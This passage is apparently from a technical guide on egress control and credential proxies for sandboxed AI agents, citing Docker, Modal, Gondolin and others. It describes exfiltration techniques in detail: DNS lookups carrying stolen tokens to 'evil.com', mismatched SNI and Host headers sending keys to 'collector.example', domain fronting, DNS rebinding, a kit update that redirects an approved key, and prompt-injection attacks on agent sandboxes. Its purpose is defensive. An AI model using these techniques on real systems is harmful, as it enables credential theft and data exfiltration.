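Some cluster networking software accepts a NetworkPolicy without enforcing it, so it is worth running the test on the cluster in question.

The gateway also helps with credential sidecars, which share their pod's network rules with the agent. With a gateway, neither container needs a direct route to GitHub, so the policy can block both. The gateway is also a safer place for the GitHub token than a mesh sidecar, but it can add the token only to requests it can read. In Istio's HTTPS example, the application encrypts the request itself and the gateway forwards it without decrypting it, so it cannot add the token.

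### Why Agyn gives each agent its own certificate

In a mesh, identity usually belongs to a service account. If a company runs 200 copies of a coding agent for different employees under one service account, all the copies share one identity. An internal service can't distinguish between them, and a key stolen from one copy can be used to impersonate any of them.

*Agyn* (Benkovich and Valkov, 2026) describes an open-source platform that gives each running copy of an agent its own identity. Benkovich and Valkov call the cluster's service mesh "too coarse" for agents and consider it unsafe to pass credentials through the language model's text, because a prompt injection could extract them. Each running agent serves one user and one task. When a message arrives for an agent that isn't running, the platform starts a pod and creates an X.509 certificate for it. After five minutes without activity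 (the default), the platform stops the pod and deletes the identity.

The agent connects to other services through OpenZiti, a private network that runs on top of the ordinary one and uses mutual TLS. The connection identifies the agent to each service before the service's own code handles the request, and access rules limit the agent to the services it needs. A sidecar in the agent's pod manages the connection.

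API keys for outside tools go only to the containers that run those tools. The agent's container never receives them. It shares a local network connection with the tools' containers, but not their files or processes.

Separate identities let operators cut off one misbehaving agent and record which agent did what, but they don't prevent an agent from misusing the access it has. Benkovich and Valkov conclude that even a compromised language model cannot leak credentials or reach unauthorised services, but their evaluation is a table comparing Agyn's features with those of four other platforms. They don't report testing the system against attacks. Istio's warnings about sidecars are a reason to test whether hostile code in the agent's container can extract the certificate's private key.

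### IETF work on workload and agent identity

SPIFFE, the cloud providers and the OAuth standards each cover part of the problem, and a request often crosses several of these systems. The Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which publishes the internet's technical standards, formed the Workload Identity in Multi-System Environments (WIMSE) working group in 2024 to address this. Its drafts describe a workload identity token that contains the program's public key. The program signs a proof for each request with the matching private key, much as in DPoP, so a stolen token is useless without that private key. The group has also worked on mutual TLS between programs.

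A separate proposal, the Identity Assertion JWT Authorization Grant (ID-JAG), covers agents that act for employees. The employee first logs in through the company's identity provider, the system that handles logins for all its applications. An agent that needs the company's issue tracker, for example, then presents proof of that login to the identity provider. If company policy allows it, the identity provider issues a signed statement addressed to the issue tracker, and the agent gives the issue tracker this statement in exchange for an access token. This lets the company decide centrally which applications each agent may use.

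Ganesan reports that business identity providers have already adopted ID-JAG for agents and that MCP uses it for employer-managed access. Its use for untrusted code is limited because the permission derives from the employee's login session, and the ID-JAG contains no evidence about where the agent is running or how well the agent protects its keys. OAuth access tokens are also bearer tokens by default, so the agent's copy still needs a proxy or a key-bound format to protect it.

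IETF drafts can change at any time, and each expires after six months unless renewed. Mutual TLS and DPoP are published standards, so someone building a system now can rely on them. Before depending on a WIMSE or ID-JAG draft, they should check its status and which version each product supports.

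## Making every outbound connection pass the checks

Proxies and brokers can protect a secret only if the sandbox's traffic must pass through them. This depends on the egress path, which means every route data can take out of the sandbox and the checks on those routes. No route may bypass the proxy, each connection must reach the service the proxy approved, and the rules must stay in force when something restarts or fails.

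A gap in the egress path is dangerous even if the sandbox starts without secrets. A program inside can still send out source code and customer data, and it may receive a secret later, in a service's reply or as a session token like the one Snowflake issues. A gap can also let the program attack other organisations. METR, an organisation that evaluates AI models, reported in August 2026 that supposedly isolated OpenAI agents had broken into Hugging Face in July during a security evaluation.

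### Leaving no route around the proxy

Many programs read their proxy settings from environment variables such as `HTTPS_PROXY`, but setting these variables doesn't force a program to use the proxy. Hostile code can ignore them and open its own connection, and some harmless programs ignore them by accident.

*Networking*, the documentation for Union.ai's sandboxes, warns that programs can bypass the product's allowlist. The allowlist mode starts one proxy for web requests and another for other traffic, such as Git and database connections, then sets variables that point to them. A program that ignores those variables avoids both proxies. For untrusted code, Union.ai recommends a mode that removes all outside connections, with the operator copying in any necessary data before the code runs.

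To allow some destinations safely, the operator has to enforce the rules outside the sandbox, where even code with administrator rights can't change them. One way is to redirect the sandbox's traffic through a firewall. Vercel's host machine does this for every outbound TCP connection and DNS query, so programs need no proxy settings (Tuttle, 2026, *A sandbox without a network boundary is only half a sandbox*).

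Another way is to give the sandbox no real network connection. Gondolin's *Network Stack* describes a host program that reads the sandbox's raw network packets and opens its own connection only for traffic it recognises as HTTP or TLS. The operator can also enable SSH and connections to particular servers. Gondolin drops everything else and blocks `CONNECT` requests, which would let a program tunnel any kind of data through HTTP. Programs that need HTTP/2 or an unusual protocol don't work with this design.

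Either design must refuse connections by default. Modal's sandboxes, like Deno's, can reach any public address until the operator restricts them. Docker prompts the user to choose a policy at first start. Its "Balanced" option refuses unlisted destinations but already allows AI providers, package managers, code hosts and common cloud services, so an operator should read the list before relying on it.

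An operator can check for these routes:

| Route | Why the proxy may miss it | What closes it | Sign that it is open |
|---|---|---|---|
| Direct TCP connection | The program ignores the proxy settings | Rules on the host that block or redirect all other connections | A request succeeds with the proxy variables removed |
| IPv6 | The operator wrote rules only for IPv4 | Matching IPv6 rules, or no IPv6 in the sandbox | A request that forces IPv6 succeeds |
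| UDP, including QUIC | The proxy handles only TCP | Dropping UDP on the host | A UDP packet reaches a test server outside |
| ICMP | It is neither TCP nor UDP | Dropping ICMP on the host | A ping reaches a test server outside |
| DNS | The resolver forwards lookups | Local answers, or an allowlist for names | A lookup reaches the name server of an unlisted test domain |
| Bypass list | The configuration exempts a destination | An empty list | Traffic to that destination is missing from the proxy's log |

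For UDP, ICMP and DNS, the test server's log is the best evidence of whether packets got out, because the sandbox's host can answer some of them itself.

Allowing a range of IP addresses can let code bypass a list of allowed domain names. On Vercel, code can connect directly to any address in an allowed range, and Vercel warns that this traffic skips both the hostname check and the credential proxy. Operators may need such a range because, as Vercel explains, its firewall can't filter unencrypted HTTP by domain. Modal similarly allows a connection that matches either the domain list or the IP list. Modal's *Networking and security* uses `52.0.0.0/8` as a sample range, which contains about 16.8 million addresses. Cloud companies rent many of these to anyone who pays, including attackers. The broadest ranges are `0.0.0.0/0` (all of IPv4) and `::/0` (all of IPv6), and an operator who removes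 one can easily forget the other.

UDP matters because some clients use HTTP/3, which runs over QUIC, a UDP-based protocol. E2B, another sandbox provider, can't filter QUIC by domain name. Dropping UDP usually causes little trouble, since most clients fall back to TCP.

Logs can reveal attempts to use a forbidden route, but they may be incomplete. Docker (2026) explains in its release notes for November 2026 that only the first 20 refused UDP destinations on each sandbox network get their own log entries, while later ones share an entry labelled `<further blocked attempts>`. Before version 0.38.0, Docker's log could also omit a blocked HTTPS connection if the program broke off the TLS handshake, according to earlier notes from Docker (2026).

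A bypass list names destinations whose traffic skips the proxy, for example because a program doesn't work through it. Blaxel's example list includes S3 and the cloud metadata service. Anyone can rent storage on S3, so hostile code could upload the project's files to an attacker's account. The exception for the metadata service is worse if the machine has a cloud role, because the code could get the role's credentials from the service.

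Products use the word "bypass" differently. Docker's *Policies* describes a log in which `forward-bypass` marks a request that went through the proxy without an added credential. Before using a bypass setting, an operator should find out whether it skips only adding the credential or also skips the destination check.

### How a DNS lookup can carry a key

Before connecting to a named server, a program normally looks up its address in the domain name system (DNS). The lookup itself can carry data. Suppose an attacker owns `evil.com` and runs the name server that answers queries about it. Hostile code in the sandbox looks up `stolen-data.evil.com`. The sandbox's resolver, the program that handles its DNS lookups, doesn't have the address, so it forwards the query. The query eventually reaches the attacker's name server, which records the name and can send instructions back in its reply. The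 sandbox never connects directly to the attacker's server during this exchange.

Docker disclosed a flaw of this kind in June 2026. According to its entry in a public catalogue of security flaws, *CVE-2026-12039* (2026), Docker Sandboxes applied the allowlist only to HTTP and HTTPS. Whenever a sandbox network was connected to the internet, its DNS server forwarded every name to the host's resolver without checking the allowlist. Docker's documentation had described the host proxy as the only way out. Sophie Lemos, who isn't on Docker's product team, found the flaw. It affected versions from 0.13.0 until the fix in 0.33.0.

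A single lookup has room for a typical key. A DNS name can have up to 253 characters including the dots, and each part between the dots, called a label, can have up to 63. GitHub's classic tokens have 40 characters. DNS treats capital and small letters as the same, so an attacker would first encode the token, for example in hexadecimal, which uses two digits for each character. The token then takes up 80 digits, which fit into two labels. With the dots and `evil.com`, the length of the name is

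63 + 1 + 17 + 1 + 8 = 90 characters.

A maximum-length name ending in `evil.com` has room for 241 hexadecimal digits, enough for 120 bytes of data. GitHub's newer fine-grained tokens have 93 characters, so they also fit into one lookup. A 12-kilobyte source file would take about 100 lookups.

Hostile code in a Docker sandbox normally has no token to send. But if a service repeats the token in a response, or a login writes another token to a file, the code can send that token out in a single DNS lookup. The proxy's log shows nothing unusual because the lookup never passes through the proxy.

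According to the pre-release notes for 0.33.0, Docker now checks lookups against the network policy. It exempts local names such as `localhost`, which some OAuth logins need. Until version 0.39.0, the check refused hosts that the operator had allowed only on an unusual port. A failed lookup can therefore mean the rules are too strict, in which case the operator should fix the rule instead of turning off the check.

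NVIDIA recommends limiting sandboxes to trusted resolvers, which prevents hostile code from sending arbitrary data to a server disguised as a resolver. But a trusted resolver will still forward a query about `evil.com` to the attacker's name server unless it filters names. On E2B, any domain rule automatically allows Google's public resolver at `8.8.8.8`, which answers queries about every domain. Operators can turn this off.

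By default, Gondolin avoids the problem by answering ordinary lookups with a made-up address and sending nothing to an outside resolver. This works because the host, not the sandbox, finds the real address when it opens the connection. Another mode forwards valid lookups to trusted resolvers, but according to Gondolin's documentation, it doesn't prevent sandboxed code from sending data out in those lookups.

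microsandbox's *DNS* describes a middle course, in which the host checks each name against the network rules before forwarding the lookup. For a forbidden name, it replies that the name doesn't exist, so the program fails promptly and no outside server sees the question.

Programs can also encrypt their DNS lookups. microsandbox can check DNS over TLS if the operator turns on TLS interception, and it blocks DNS over QUIC. It can't distinguish DNS over HTTPS from other web traffic, so the operator has to leave DNS-over-HTTPS servers off the allowlist.

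### Checking where a connection really goes

When a program uses an intercepting proxy, its request names the destination in three places: the `CONNECT` request, the SNI field of the TLS handshake, and the HTTP `Host` header. An honest client writes the same name in all of them, but hostile code can send this:

```
CONNECT:  api.github.com:443
SNI:      api.github.com
Host:     collector.example
```

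If the proxy used the `CONNECT` name to select the GitHub token and the `Host` header to decide where to send the request, it would deliver the token to `collector.example`. The proxy should refuse any request in which the names differ. It has to check every request, because a program can send many requests over one connection and change the `Host` header each time.

Two names can also be spelled differently and refer to the same host. DNS ignores case, and a name may end with a dot, so `API.GitHub.com` and `api.github.com.` both refer to `api.github.com`. If the part of the proxy that checks the rules reads a name differently from the part that opens the connection, hostile code may be able to exploit the difference. Tuttle lists this as one way untrusted code can get past a sandbox's network controls. The safest design converts the name to a standard form once and uses that form to check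 the rules, select the credential and open the connection.

A firewall that doesn't decrypt HTTPS traffic can't read a request's `Host` header. Modal's domain filter, for example, checks only the SNI. Many websites share servers run by a content delivery network, which uses the `Host` header to determine which site should answer. Hostile code can therefore get past such a filter by putting an allowed site in the SNI and an attacker's site on the same network in the header, a technique called domain fronting. Some networks reject such requests, but the operator can't rely on that.

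Encrypted Client Hello, a newer addition to TLS, hides the real site name, so the firewall sees only a public name belonging to the hosting provider. Modal checks that public name against its allowlist and blocks the connection unless the operator has allowed it. Allowing that name would admit every site hidden behind it.

Even when all the names agree, hostile code can connect to an attacker's server at `203.0.113.5` and write `api.github.com` in the SNI. A firewall that checks the name but forwards the connection to the address the sandbox chose would send the data to the attacker. Modal prevents this by doing its own lookup of the name and ignoring the sandbox's address. microsandbox accepts an address under a domain rule only if an earlier lookup of that domain from the same sandbox returned it.

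The proxy also protects the credential by checking the server's certificate on its second connection. An attacker's server can't present a valid certificate for `api.github.com`, so the proxy refuses to send it the token. This doesn't help when the firewall passes encrypted traffic through unread, because then only the hostile program checks the certificate.

If an operator turns off the certificate check to get an internal service working, they may not notice the danger, because every request succeeds. With the check on, a bad certificate causes a visible error. Since version 0.51.0, when a connection to a service fails, Docker's proxy returns a 502 error that names the host and the reason.

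A permitted name can also lead to a forbidden address. In an attack called DNS rebinding, a domain's owner makes DNS return a public address when the proxy checks the name, then the metadata service's address, `169.254.169.254`, when the proxy connects. Gondolin refuses internal addresses by default and checks the address again when it opens the connection. It doesn't check again when a later request reuses the connection, which is reasonable because the connection still leads to the address that passed. Gondolin also checks the target of each redirect, so an approved site can't send the proxy to an internal one.

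The list of forbidden addresses must cover whole ranges. Union.ai warns that blocking only `169.254.169.254` misses the rest of that local range and the IPv6 metadata addresses. Blocking by name is also not enough, because one address can have several names. Docker's documentation for an older version of its product describes how the proxy blocks `ip6-localhost`, another name for the local machine, by checking the address it resolves to.

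### Keeping the rules in force after a restart or failure

A second Docker flaw from June 2026 concerned ICMP, the protocol that networks use for pings and error messages. A ping can carry more than a thousand bytes of arbitrary data, so hostile code can put a whole key in one packet. Docker's documentation promised that sandboxes could not send ICMP to the outside. Docker's *CVE-2026-12539* (2026) explains how this protection disappeared:

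1. Docker created a sandbox's network and attached the check that refused ICMP. At this point, a ping to an outside address failed as it should.
2. The Docker daemon, the background program that manages the sandboxes, restarted.
3. The daemon rebuilt the network from its saved settings but did not attach the ICMP check again.
4. The sandbox could now send pings to any address, regardless of its allowlist.

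Docker's staff found the flaw, which affected versions from 0.14.0 until 0.33.0. Docker rated both June flaws as medium severity. CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, recorded no known exploitation of either when Docker published them.

Testing the ICMP block only on a new sandbox would have missed the flaw. Operators need to repeat the test after restarting the sandbox, the daemon and the host machine. The start-up code should build every check from the saved settings each time it runs, and keep the sandbox offline until the checks are running.

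Docker later fixed another restart flaw, CVE-2026-126330, that affected incoming connections. Before version 0.53.0, a port the operator had closed could reopen when the sandbox restarted if Docker had assigned the port number automatically.

Moving a sandbox can also change its rules. Docker's *Manage cloud network policy* warns that Docker doesn't copy a computer's local rules to cloud sandboxes, so the operator must set and test them again. If a rule change on a running sandbox affects only new connections, hostile code can keep using a connection it opened earlier. Modal avoids this by closing existing connections that a new policy forbids.

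The egress path must also fail closed, meaning that traffic stops when the proxy stops. This happens automatically if the proxy is the sandbox's only route out. If the system falls back to a direct connection, a proxy crash removes the restrictions while the agent continues to work normally, so nobody has a reason to investigate. The operator can test for this fault by stopping the proxy and checking that every outbound request fails.

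Missing settings can have the same effect as a crashed proxy. Anthropic's Sandbox Runtime, a tool that restricts programs without putting them in a container, had such a bug. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-66479* (2025), a record from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, reports that versions before 0.0.16 did not properly enforce network restrictions if the operator had listed no allowed domains. An operator might have left the list empty to block everything. Vercel treats an empty policy as a complete block, including DNS, but still advises operators who want this to select its `deny-all` mode.

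### Allowed services with their own internet access

An allowlist controls which services a sandbox can connect to, but not what those services do next. Suppose a sandbox can connect only to a company's build server, which runs any code the agent sends it and has unrestricted internet access. Hostile code in the sandbox can send the project's files to the build server along with a script that uploads them to an attacker. The sandbox can therefore in effect reach the whole internet, even though it connects only to an allowed server.

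A package mirror that downloads from any address it receives creates the same problem, and so does a language-model service that can fetch web pages. Tuttle warns that attackers can turn a trusted package service into a relay. In Docker's DNS flaw, the host's resolver relayed data to servers that the sandbox could not contact directly.

This kind of leak is hard to see from the sandbox. The proxy's log shows ordinary requests to an approved host, and only the other service's records can show where the data went.

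Before allowing a service, the operator should find out whether it can run code, fetch URLs or publish data for its users. Docker warns that allowing `github.com` gives the sandbox access to everything on that domain, including content from strangers. If a service has a feature that can relay data, the operator can turn the feature off or restrict the service's own outbound connections.

The operator can also allow a service only while the agent needs it. Cloudflare's *Secure credential injection and dynamic egress policies for Sandboxes* gives the example of a sandbox that can reach GitHub and npm while it installs packages. The operator's program then blocks all the sandbox's HTTP requests, so the agent can't use either service as a relay once it starts its main work. A service that the agent uses throughout, such as its model provider, has to stay reachable, so any web-fetching tool that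 service offers needs its own restrictions.

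## Deciding where each credential may go and what it may do

Even when every request passes through the proxy and reaches the server it names, the operator still has to decide which requests should carry a secret. An allowlist doesn't settle this, because most of the hosts on it have no reason to receive any given secret. The coding agent from the GitHub example might need these four:

| Host | Why the agent connects | GitHub token | Model provider's key |
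|---|---|---|---|
| `api.github.com` | To open the pull request | Yes | No |
| `github.com` | To push the branch | Yes | No |
| `registry.npmjs.org` | To download packages | No | No |
| `api.anthropic.com` | To use its language model | No | Yes |

If the proxy used one list for both decisions, it would send the GitHub token to npm and Anthropic as well. Neither is likely to misuse the token, but either might log it. Any package mirror or documentation site that the operator later allowed would also receive the token.

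Docker's kits, which are packaged configurations for agents, list the hosts an agent may reach separately from the hosts each credential may be sent to. The proxy adds a secret to a request only if both lists allow the host. The built-in `github` service, for example, doesn't cover `npm.pkg.github.com`, where GitHub hosts npm packages. Docker tells operators who need private packages from there to set up a custom secret for that host.

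### Writing a destination binding

A destination binding should refuse everything by default and then name the requests that need the secret. In a notation made up for this example, the binding for the GitHub token could be:

```
secret: github-token-acme-shop
default: refuse
allow:
  POST https://api.github.com:443/repos/acme/shop/pulls
  GET  https://github.com:443/acme/shop.git/info/refs
  POST https://github.com:443/acme/shop.git/git-upload-pack
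  POST https://github.com:443/acme/shop.git/git-receive-pack
```

The first rule opens pull requests. The other three let Git download from one repository and push to it.

The proxy should compare the whole host name. A rule that accepts any name ending in `github.com` also accepts `notgithub.com`, which an attacker could register. The proxy should also check the port, because one machine can run several programs, and a debugging tool on port 8080 might display every header it receives.

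The binding should also require HTTPS. Docker adds stored credentials only to HTTPS requests. It still forwards plain HTTP requests if the network policy allows them, but without the secret.

Paths need the same care as host names. A rule that covers every path beginning with `/repos/acme/shop` also covers `/repos/acme/shop-payroll`, so the match has to end at a slash or at the end of the path. Hostile code can also request `/repos/acme/shop/../payroll`, which some servers interpret as `/repos/acme/payroll`. The proxy should convert the path to a standard form before checking it, then send that same form to the service.

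Docker is strict about paths in one case, when a private container registry handles logins on a separate server. The operator must approve that server's address before the proxy sends it the registry password. If the operator approves `https://gitlab.example.com/jwt/auth`, the proxy refuses the same address with a slash at the end.

Docker has ignored case when matching paths and query strings against ordinary HTTP rules since version 0.53.0, according to its release notes. This stops hostile code from evading a ban on `/repos/acme/shop` by writing `/repos/Acme/Shop`, which GitHub treats as the same repository. But on a service where `/Reports` and `/reports` are different pages, a rule that allows one now allows both.

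### What broad bindings cost

Docker's documentation lists 11 built-in services, and their credentials can go to a total of 31 hosts. The GitHub token alone can go to six:

```
api.github.com              gist.github.com
github.com                  copilot.github.com
raw.githubusercontent.com   api.githubcopilot.com
```

An agent that only pushes a branch and opens a pull request needs just the first two hosts in the left column. GitHub runs all six, so allowing them all doesn't send the token to a third party, but each additional host gives hostile code more features to misuse and more places where the token might end up in a log. Docker uses the longer list because it can't know in advance which GitHub features an agent will use, but an operator who does know can write a shorter one.

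Wildcards are riskier because they can include hosts that belong to other people. In Docker's custom secrets, `*.example.com` covers names with one extra label, such as `api.example.com`, and `**.example.com` covers names with any number. Suppose a company runs an internal service at `acme-api.vercel.app`, and the operator binds the service's key to `*.vercel.app`. Vercel lets anyone publish a program under that domain. An attacker could publish one, have hostile code in the sandbox call it, and read the key from the request.

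A wildcard for the company's own domain is safer but can still expose secrets. The company may have a forgotten subdomain, such as `old-demo.acme.com`, that points to a hosting account it closed. If the hosting provider lets someone else claim that subdomain, they can receive any secret bound to `*.acme.com`.

As described earlier, Daytona lets a secret with no set destination go anywhere. Since version 0.51.0, Docker has refused to substitute custom secrets that have no destination host. Docker has warned that refusing by default offers less protection than it seems to when the list of exceptions is long, according to @IT's *人が「承認」した無害なコマンドでAIが乗っ取られる コードエディタCursorを襲った“2行の攻撃*, a Japanese article about Docker's series on coding agents.

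### How a changed kit could redirect an approved key

Docker Sandboxes asked users to approve the destinations for each secret and saved their answers. But for 11 weeks in 2026, the proxy didn't check those destinations before sending a key. Peyton Kennedy, a researcher at the security company Endor Labs, found the flaw and announced it on 30 November in the company's *CVE-2026-136998*. The flaw affected versions from 0.43.0, released on 15 September, until 0.55.0, which Docker released on the day of the announcement.

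The flaw concerned kits from outside Docker, which a user can fetch from a registry, a Git repository or a local folder. The Hacker News' *Docker Sandboxes Flaw Lets Malicious AI Agent Kit Updates Steal Developers' API* (2026), an article from a security news site unrelated to the Hacker News forum, describes how an attack would work:

1. A developer runs a third-party kit for the first time. The kit asks to use the developer's Anthropic key at `api.anthropic.com`, and the developer agrees.
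2. Docker saves the approval in a file on the host:

```
bindings:
  anthropic:
    apiKey:
      domains: [api.anthropic.com]
```

3. The kit's author publishes a new version at the same address, changing the key's destination to a server such as `collector.example`.
4. The developer creates another sandbox. Docker finds an approval for `anthropic` and doesn't ask again.
5. Code in the sandbox sends a request to `collector.example`. The proxy takes the destination from the new version of the kit and adds the real key.

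In simplified form, the proxy applied the first of these rules when it should have applied the second:

```
Before 0.55.0:
  if approvals has an entry for "anthropic"
  and the current kit lists this host: add the key

Since 0.55.0:
  if approvals["anthropic"].apiKey.domains lists this host
  and the current kit lists this host: add the key
```

The network allowlist did not protect the key, because a new version of the kit could add the attacker's server to it without prompting the user. Docker had separate settings for where the sandbox could connect and where the key could go, but the same untrusted file controlled both.

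Kennedy demonstrated the attack with a dummy Anthropic key and a test server on his own machine. The server received the key in cleartext, and the approval remained in effect after he deleted the sandbox. Requiring HTTPS would not prevent the attack, because an attacker can get a valid certificate for a domain they own.

The log recorded that the connection was allowed but not that the proxy had added a key. An administrator would have seen what IT之家, a Chinese technology site, describes as an ordinary entry, with an unfamiliar host name as the only clue. A credential proxy should therefore log the name, but not the value, of the secret it adds to each request.

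Thirteen built-in services shared the faulty code: Anthropic, Copilot, Cursor, Devin, Droid, GitHub, Google, Groq, Mistral, Nebius, OpenAI, OpenRouter and xAI. Kennedy tested only the Anthropic service. Docker makes service secrets available to every sandbox by default, so the stolen key would often be the one the developer used for all their agents. Nobody has established whether Docker's cloud sandboxes, which store secrets separately, ever had the flaw.

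Kennedy gave the flaw 6.9 and Docker gave it 5.6 on version 4.0 of CVSS, the standard ten-point scale for the severity of security flaws. They disagree about whether to count the harm an attacker could do to the victim's account at Anthropic or GitHub. Kennedy first gave the flaw 9.3 on the older version 3.1, then lowered the score to 8.2 because the developer has to fetch the malicious kit. The Hacker News found no reports of attacks.

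A contradiction in Docker's earlier documentation hinted at the flaw. Docker promised to ask for approval again if a kit requested hosts that the existing approval didn't cover, but also said that an `apiKey` entry alone authorised use of the key. Kits in the oldest format could use the credentials they declared without any approval.

Version 0.55.0 checks the approved destinations, with separate lists for API keys and OAuth tokens. It treats an approval that lists no destinations as missing. According to Docker's current documentation, third-party kits in every format now need approval, and a kit that requests a new host triggers a new prompt. If nobody is there to answer, as in an automated build, a sandbox without an approval starts without the credential.

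PCQuest advises users to upgrade, review the permissions of their third-party kits, replace any key that may have leaked, and check their bills and repositories for unexpected activity. Anyone who updated a third-party kit on an affected version has good reason to replace the keys that kit used, because the log can't show whether the proxy sent those keys elsewhere.

### Checking the secret and destination on every use

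An approval should cover a secret and its destination together, and the proxy should check both each time it adds the secret. For example, if the approval is "This kit may send the Anthropic key to `api.anthropic.com`", the proxy can compare that destination with the one in the request. "This kit may use the Anthropic key" is too broad because it names no destination. The approval must also be stored where neither the kit nor the sandbox can change it.

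Checking only when the sandbox starts isn't enough, because the configuration may change later. For a similar reason, Docker's sandboxes lost their ICMP block after a restart.

The identity behind a credential can change too. SC Media's *Docker Hub critical vulnerability allowed token misuse* describes a flaw in Docker Hub that let an attacker turn an account into an organisation and name another user as its owner. The attacker's existing access token then worked as that user's token, without the user's consent. Docker fixed the flaw within four hours of receiving a report on 30 September 2026 and found no evidence that anyone had exploited it.

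Even with these checks, a new version of a kit can misuse the key at an approved destination. An operator can reduce this risk by pinning the kit to an exact version, such as a Git commit, and reviewing the changes before updating.

### When hostile code brings its own key

Destination binding controls where the operator's secrets go, but it has no effect on a secret the attacker supplies. Hostile code can use a token for the attacker's own GitHub account to upload the developer's source code to that account through an allowed host, even though the developer's token stays safe.

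The security researcher Johann Rehberger demonstrated this kind of attack in October 2025 on the sandbox where Anthropic's Claude runs code. The sandbox's default allowlist included Anthropic's API. A prompt injection supplied the attacker's Anthropic API key, and the code used it to upload the user's data to the attacker's account. Lasso Security ran a related test on OpenShell, another sandbox for agents, and got sensitive data out through routes that the default configuration permitted. Lasso notes that OpenShell's policies control where data can go but don't account for why an agent is sending it.

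The proxy should remove or refuse any credential the program supplies. Removing it is more convenient, because many clients send a dummy key and will work once the proxy replaces it with the real one. Refusing the request warns the operator. A proxy can do both by replacing the dummy value it issued and refusing any other credential.

Header injection overwrites the program's credential on hosts for which the proxy has a secret, but leaves it unchanged on other hosts. For example, the coding agent can download packages from `registry.npmjs.org` without a secret, so the proxy has none to inject. Hostile code can then send the registry an attacker's npm token and publish the developer's source code as a package. To prevent this, the proxy can remove authentication headers from requests to the registry and allow only downloads, which use the `GET` method.

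This requires TLS interception, which many proxies use only for connections that need a credential. On other connections, the proxy can't see whose account the program is using. For each host that doesn't need a credential, the operator has to choose between intercepting the connection and accepting that data can leave through it. A company can avoid this choice for packages by running its own download-only mirror.

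Docker's proxy removes headers such as `Authorization` and `x-api-key` on routes where the user hasn't approved a kit's use of a credential. It doesn't remove credentials from plain HTTP requests, so an operator worried about this kind of leak should also block plain HTTP.

Removing authentication headers doesn't remove every credential, because a program can also send credentials in cookies, query strings or request bodies. For example, an attacker can create a presigned S3 URL for their own storage, which lets the sandbox upload a file there without an authentication header. For services that accept such credentials, the proxy needs rules about the account or storage bucket in the request. Some large services can block outside accounts themselves. Microsoft, for example, lets a company's proxy add a header listing the organisations whose accounts may log in, and refuses all others.

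### Misusing a key without reading it

The remaining danger is a request that uses the operator's own credential at the right service for a harmful purpose. Suppose hostile code in the sandbox sends this:

```
DELETE /repos/acme/shop/git/refs/heads/release HTTP/1.1
Host: api.github.com
Authorization: Bearer not-a-real-token
```

When hostile code sends GitHub a request to delete the `release` branch, a proxy that checks only the host replaces the dummy value in the request with the developer's token. The token is valid and has permission to change the repository, so GitHub deletes the branch, even though the code never saw the token.

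Security researchers call this the confused deputy problem. The name comes from a 1988 paper by Norm Hardy about a compiler that had permission to write to a file of billing records. A user who lacked that permission told the compiler to save its debugging output under the billing file's name, and the compiler used its own permission to overwrite the records. A credential proxy is in the same position, since it holds a permission that the sandbox lacks and takes instructions from the sandbox.

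Operators have four main ways to limit the damage. The table shows how each handles five harmful requests, assuming the GitHub token works for one repository and can change its files and pull requests but not its settings.

| Harmful request | Narrow token | Method and path rules | Rate and spending limits | Human approval |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Delete the repository | Blocks it | Block it | Allow it | Can block it |
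| Delete a branch through the API | Allows it | Block it | Allow it | Can block it |
| Delete a branch with `git push` | Allows it | Allow it | Allow it | Can block it if the prompt shows what the push does |
| Put private data in a public pull request | Allows it | Allow it | Allow it | Can block it if the person notices the data |
| Run up a large bill with the model provider | Allows it | Allow it | Cap the loss | Impractical for so many requests |

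### Narrow tokens

A narrow token is the best place to start because the service itself enforces the limit, even if the proxy has a bug or someone steals the token and uses it elsewhere. In the decoy experiment, the bots ran up no charges on restricted keys and could apparently tell them from unrestricted ones, according to Help Net Security.

A token can only be as narrow as the service's permissions allow. GitHub's permission to change a repository's contents covers both pushing and deleting branches, so an agent that needs to push gets a token that can also delete. Some services offer only one key, with full access.

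Convenience also leads people to use broader tokens than they need. Docker's documentation suggests supplying the GitHub secret with the command `gh auth token`, which prints the token that the developer's own GitHub program uses. According to Kennedy, a typical developer token can write to all of that developer's repositories. A token limited to one repository takes a few minutes longer to set up and exposes much less.

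### Method and path rules

The proxy can restrict requests more finely than the service's permissions do. The binding for `acme/shop` allows `POST` requests to `/repos/acme/shop/pulls` but blocks the `DELETE` request, although the token would permit both.

These rules work well when each operation has its own address, but many interfaces don't work that way. GitHub also offers a GraphQL API, where every operation is a `POST` request to `/graphql` and the body determines what happens. A rule that allows `/graphql` allows every operation the token permits. Blocking `/graphql` breaks GitHub's command-line program, which uses GraphQL to create pull requests, so the agent would have to call the ordinary API instead.

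Git has a similar problem. An ordinary push, a push that overwrites history and a push that deletes a branch all use `POST` and the same path, so the proxy would have to interpret Git's data format to distinguish them. It is easier to turn on branch protection at GitHub, which can forbid deletions and overwrites on chosen branches even when the token has write access.

Some services also accept a header that changes a request's method, so a request can pass through the proxy as a `POST` and run on the service as a `DELETE`. The proxy should remove such headers.

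### Rate and spending limits

Rate limits cap the number of requests in a given period, and spending limits cap the cost. They matter most for language models and other services that charge for use. The decoy experiment shows why counting requests isn't enough. The 143 requests that emptied an OpenAI account in under a day used more than 18 million input tokens. (Here, tokens are the pieces of text by which model providers charge, not credentials.) The average request contained about

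18,000,000 / 143 ≈ 126,000 tokens.

Spread over a day, this is only about six requests an hour, so a limit of 60 requests an hour would never have taken effect, while a limit on tokens or money would have.

The operator should set a spending limit at the model provider as well as at the proxy. The proxy can set a separate limit for each sandbox, but it can't count requests made elsewhere with a stolen key. Each limit has to be high enough for the agent's normal work, so an attacker can still spend up to that amount. Neither limit prevents a single destructive request, such as deleting a branch.

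### Human approval

A person can judge things that a rule can't, such as whether anyone asked for the `release` branch to be deleted. Because of approval fatigue, though, human review works best for a few rare actions that are hard to undo.

A careful person can also approve something harmful because the prompt doesn't show everything that matters. Docker describes a flaw in Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, that let hostile text change environment variables without the developer's knowledge. The prompt then accurately showed `git branch`, a normally harmless command that lists branches, but when the developer approved it, the changed variables made it run the attacker's code.

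A credential proxy can avoid this problem by asking about the final request instead of the command that produced it. In the branch example, the proxy would hold the `DELETE` request and show the person this:

```
Delete branch "release" from acme/shop?
Sandbox: fix-rounding     Secret: github-token-acme-shop
```

The prompt should appear outside the sandbox, and the proxy should write it from the request itself, because hostile code could supply a misleading description. If the person agrees, the proxy should send exactly the request it held, and only once. The approval should expire quickly. In Docker, a kit's request for a different permission, to open a port on the developer's computer, expires after 45 seconds if it needs approval. CapSeal goes further by tying each permission to one session and one narrowly defined action.

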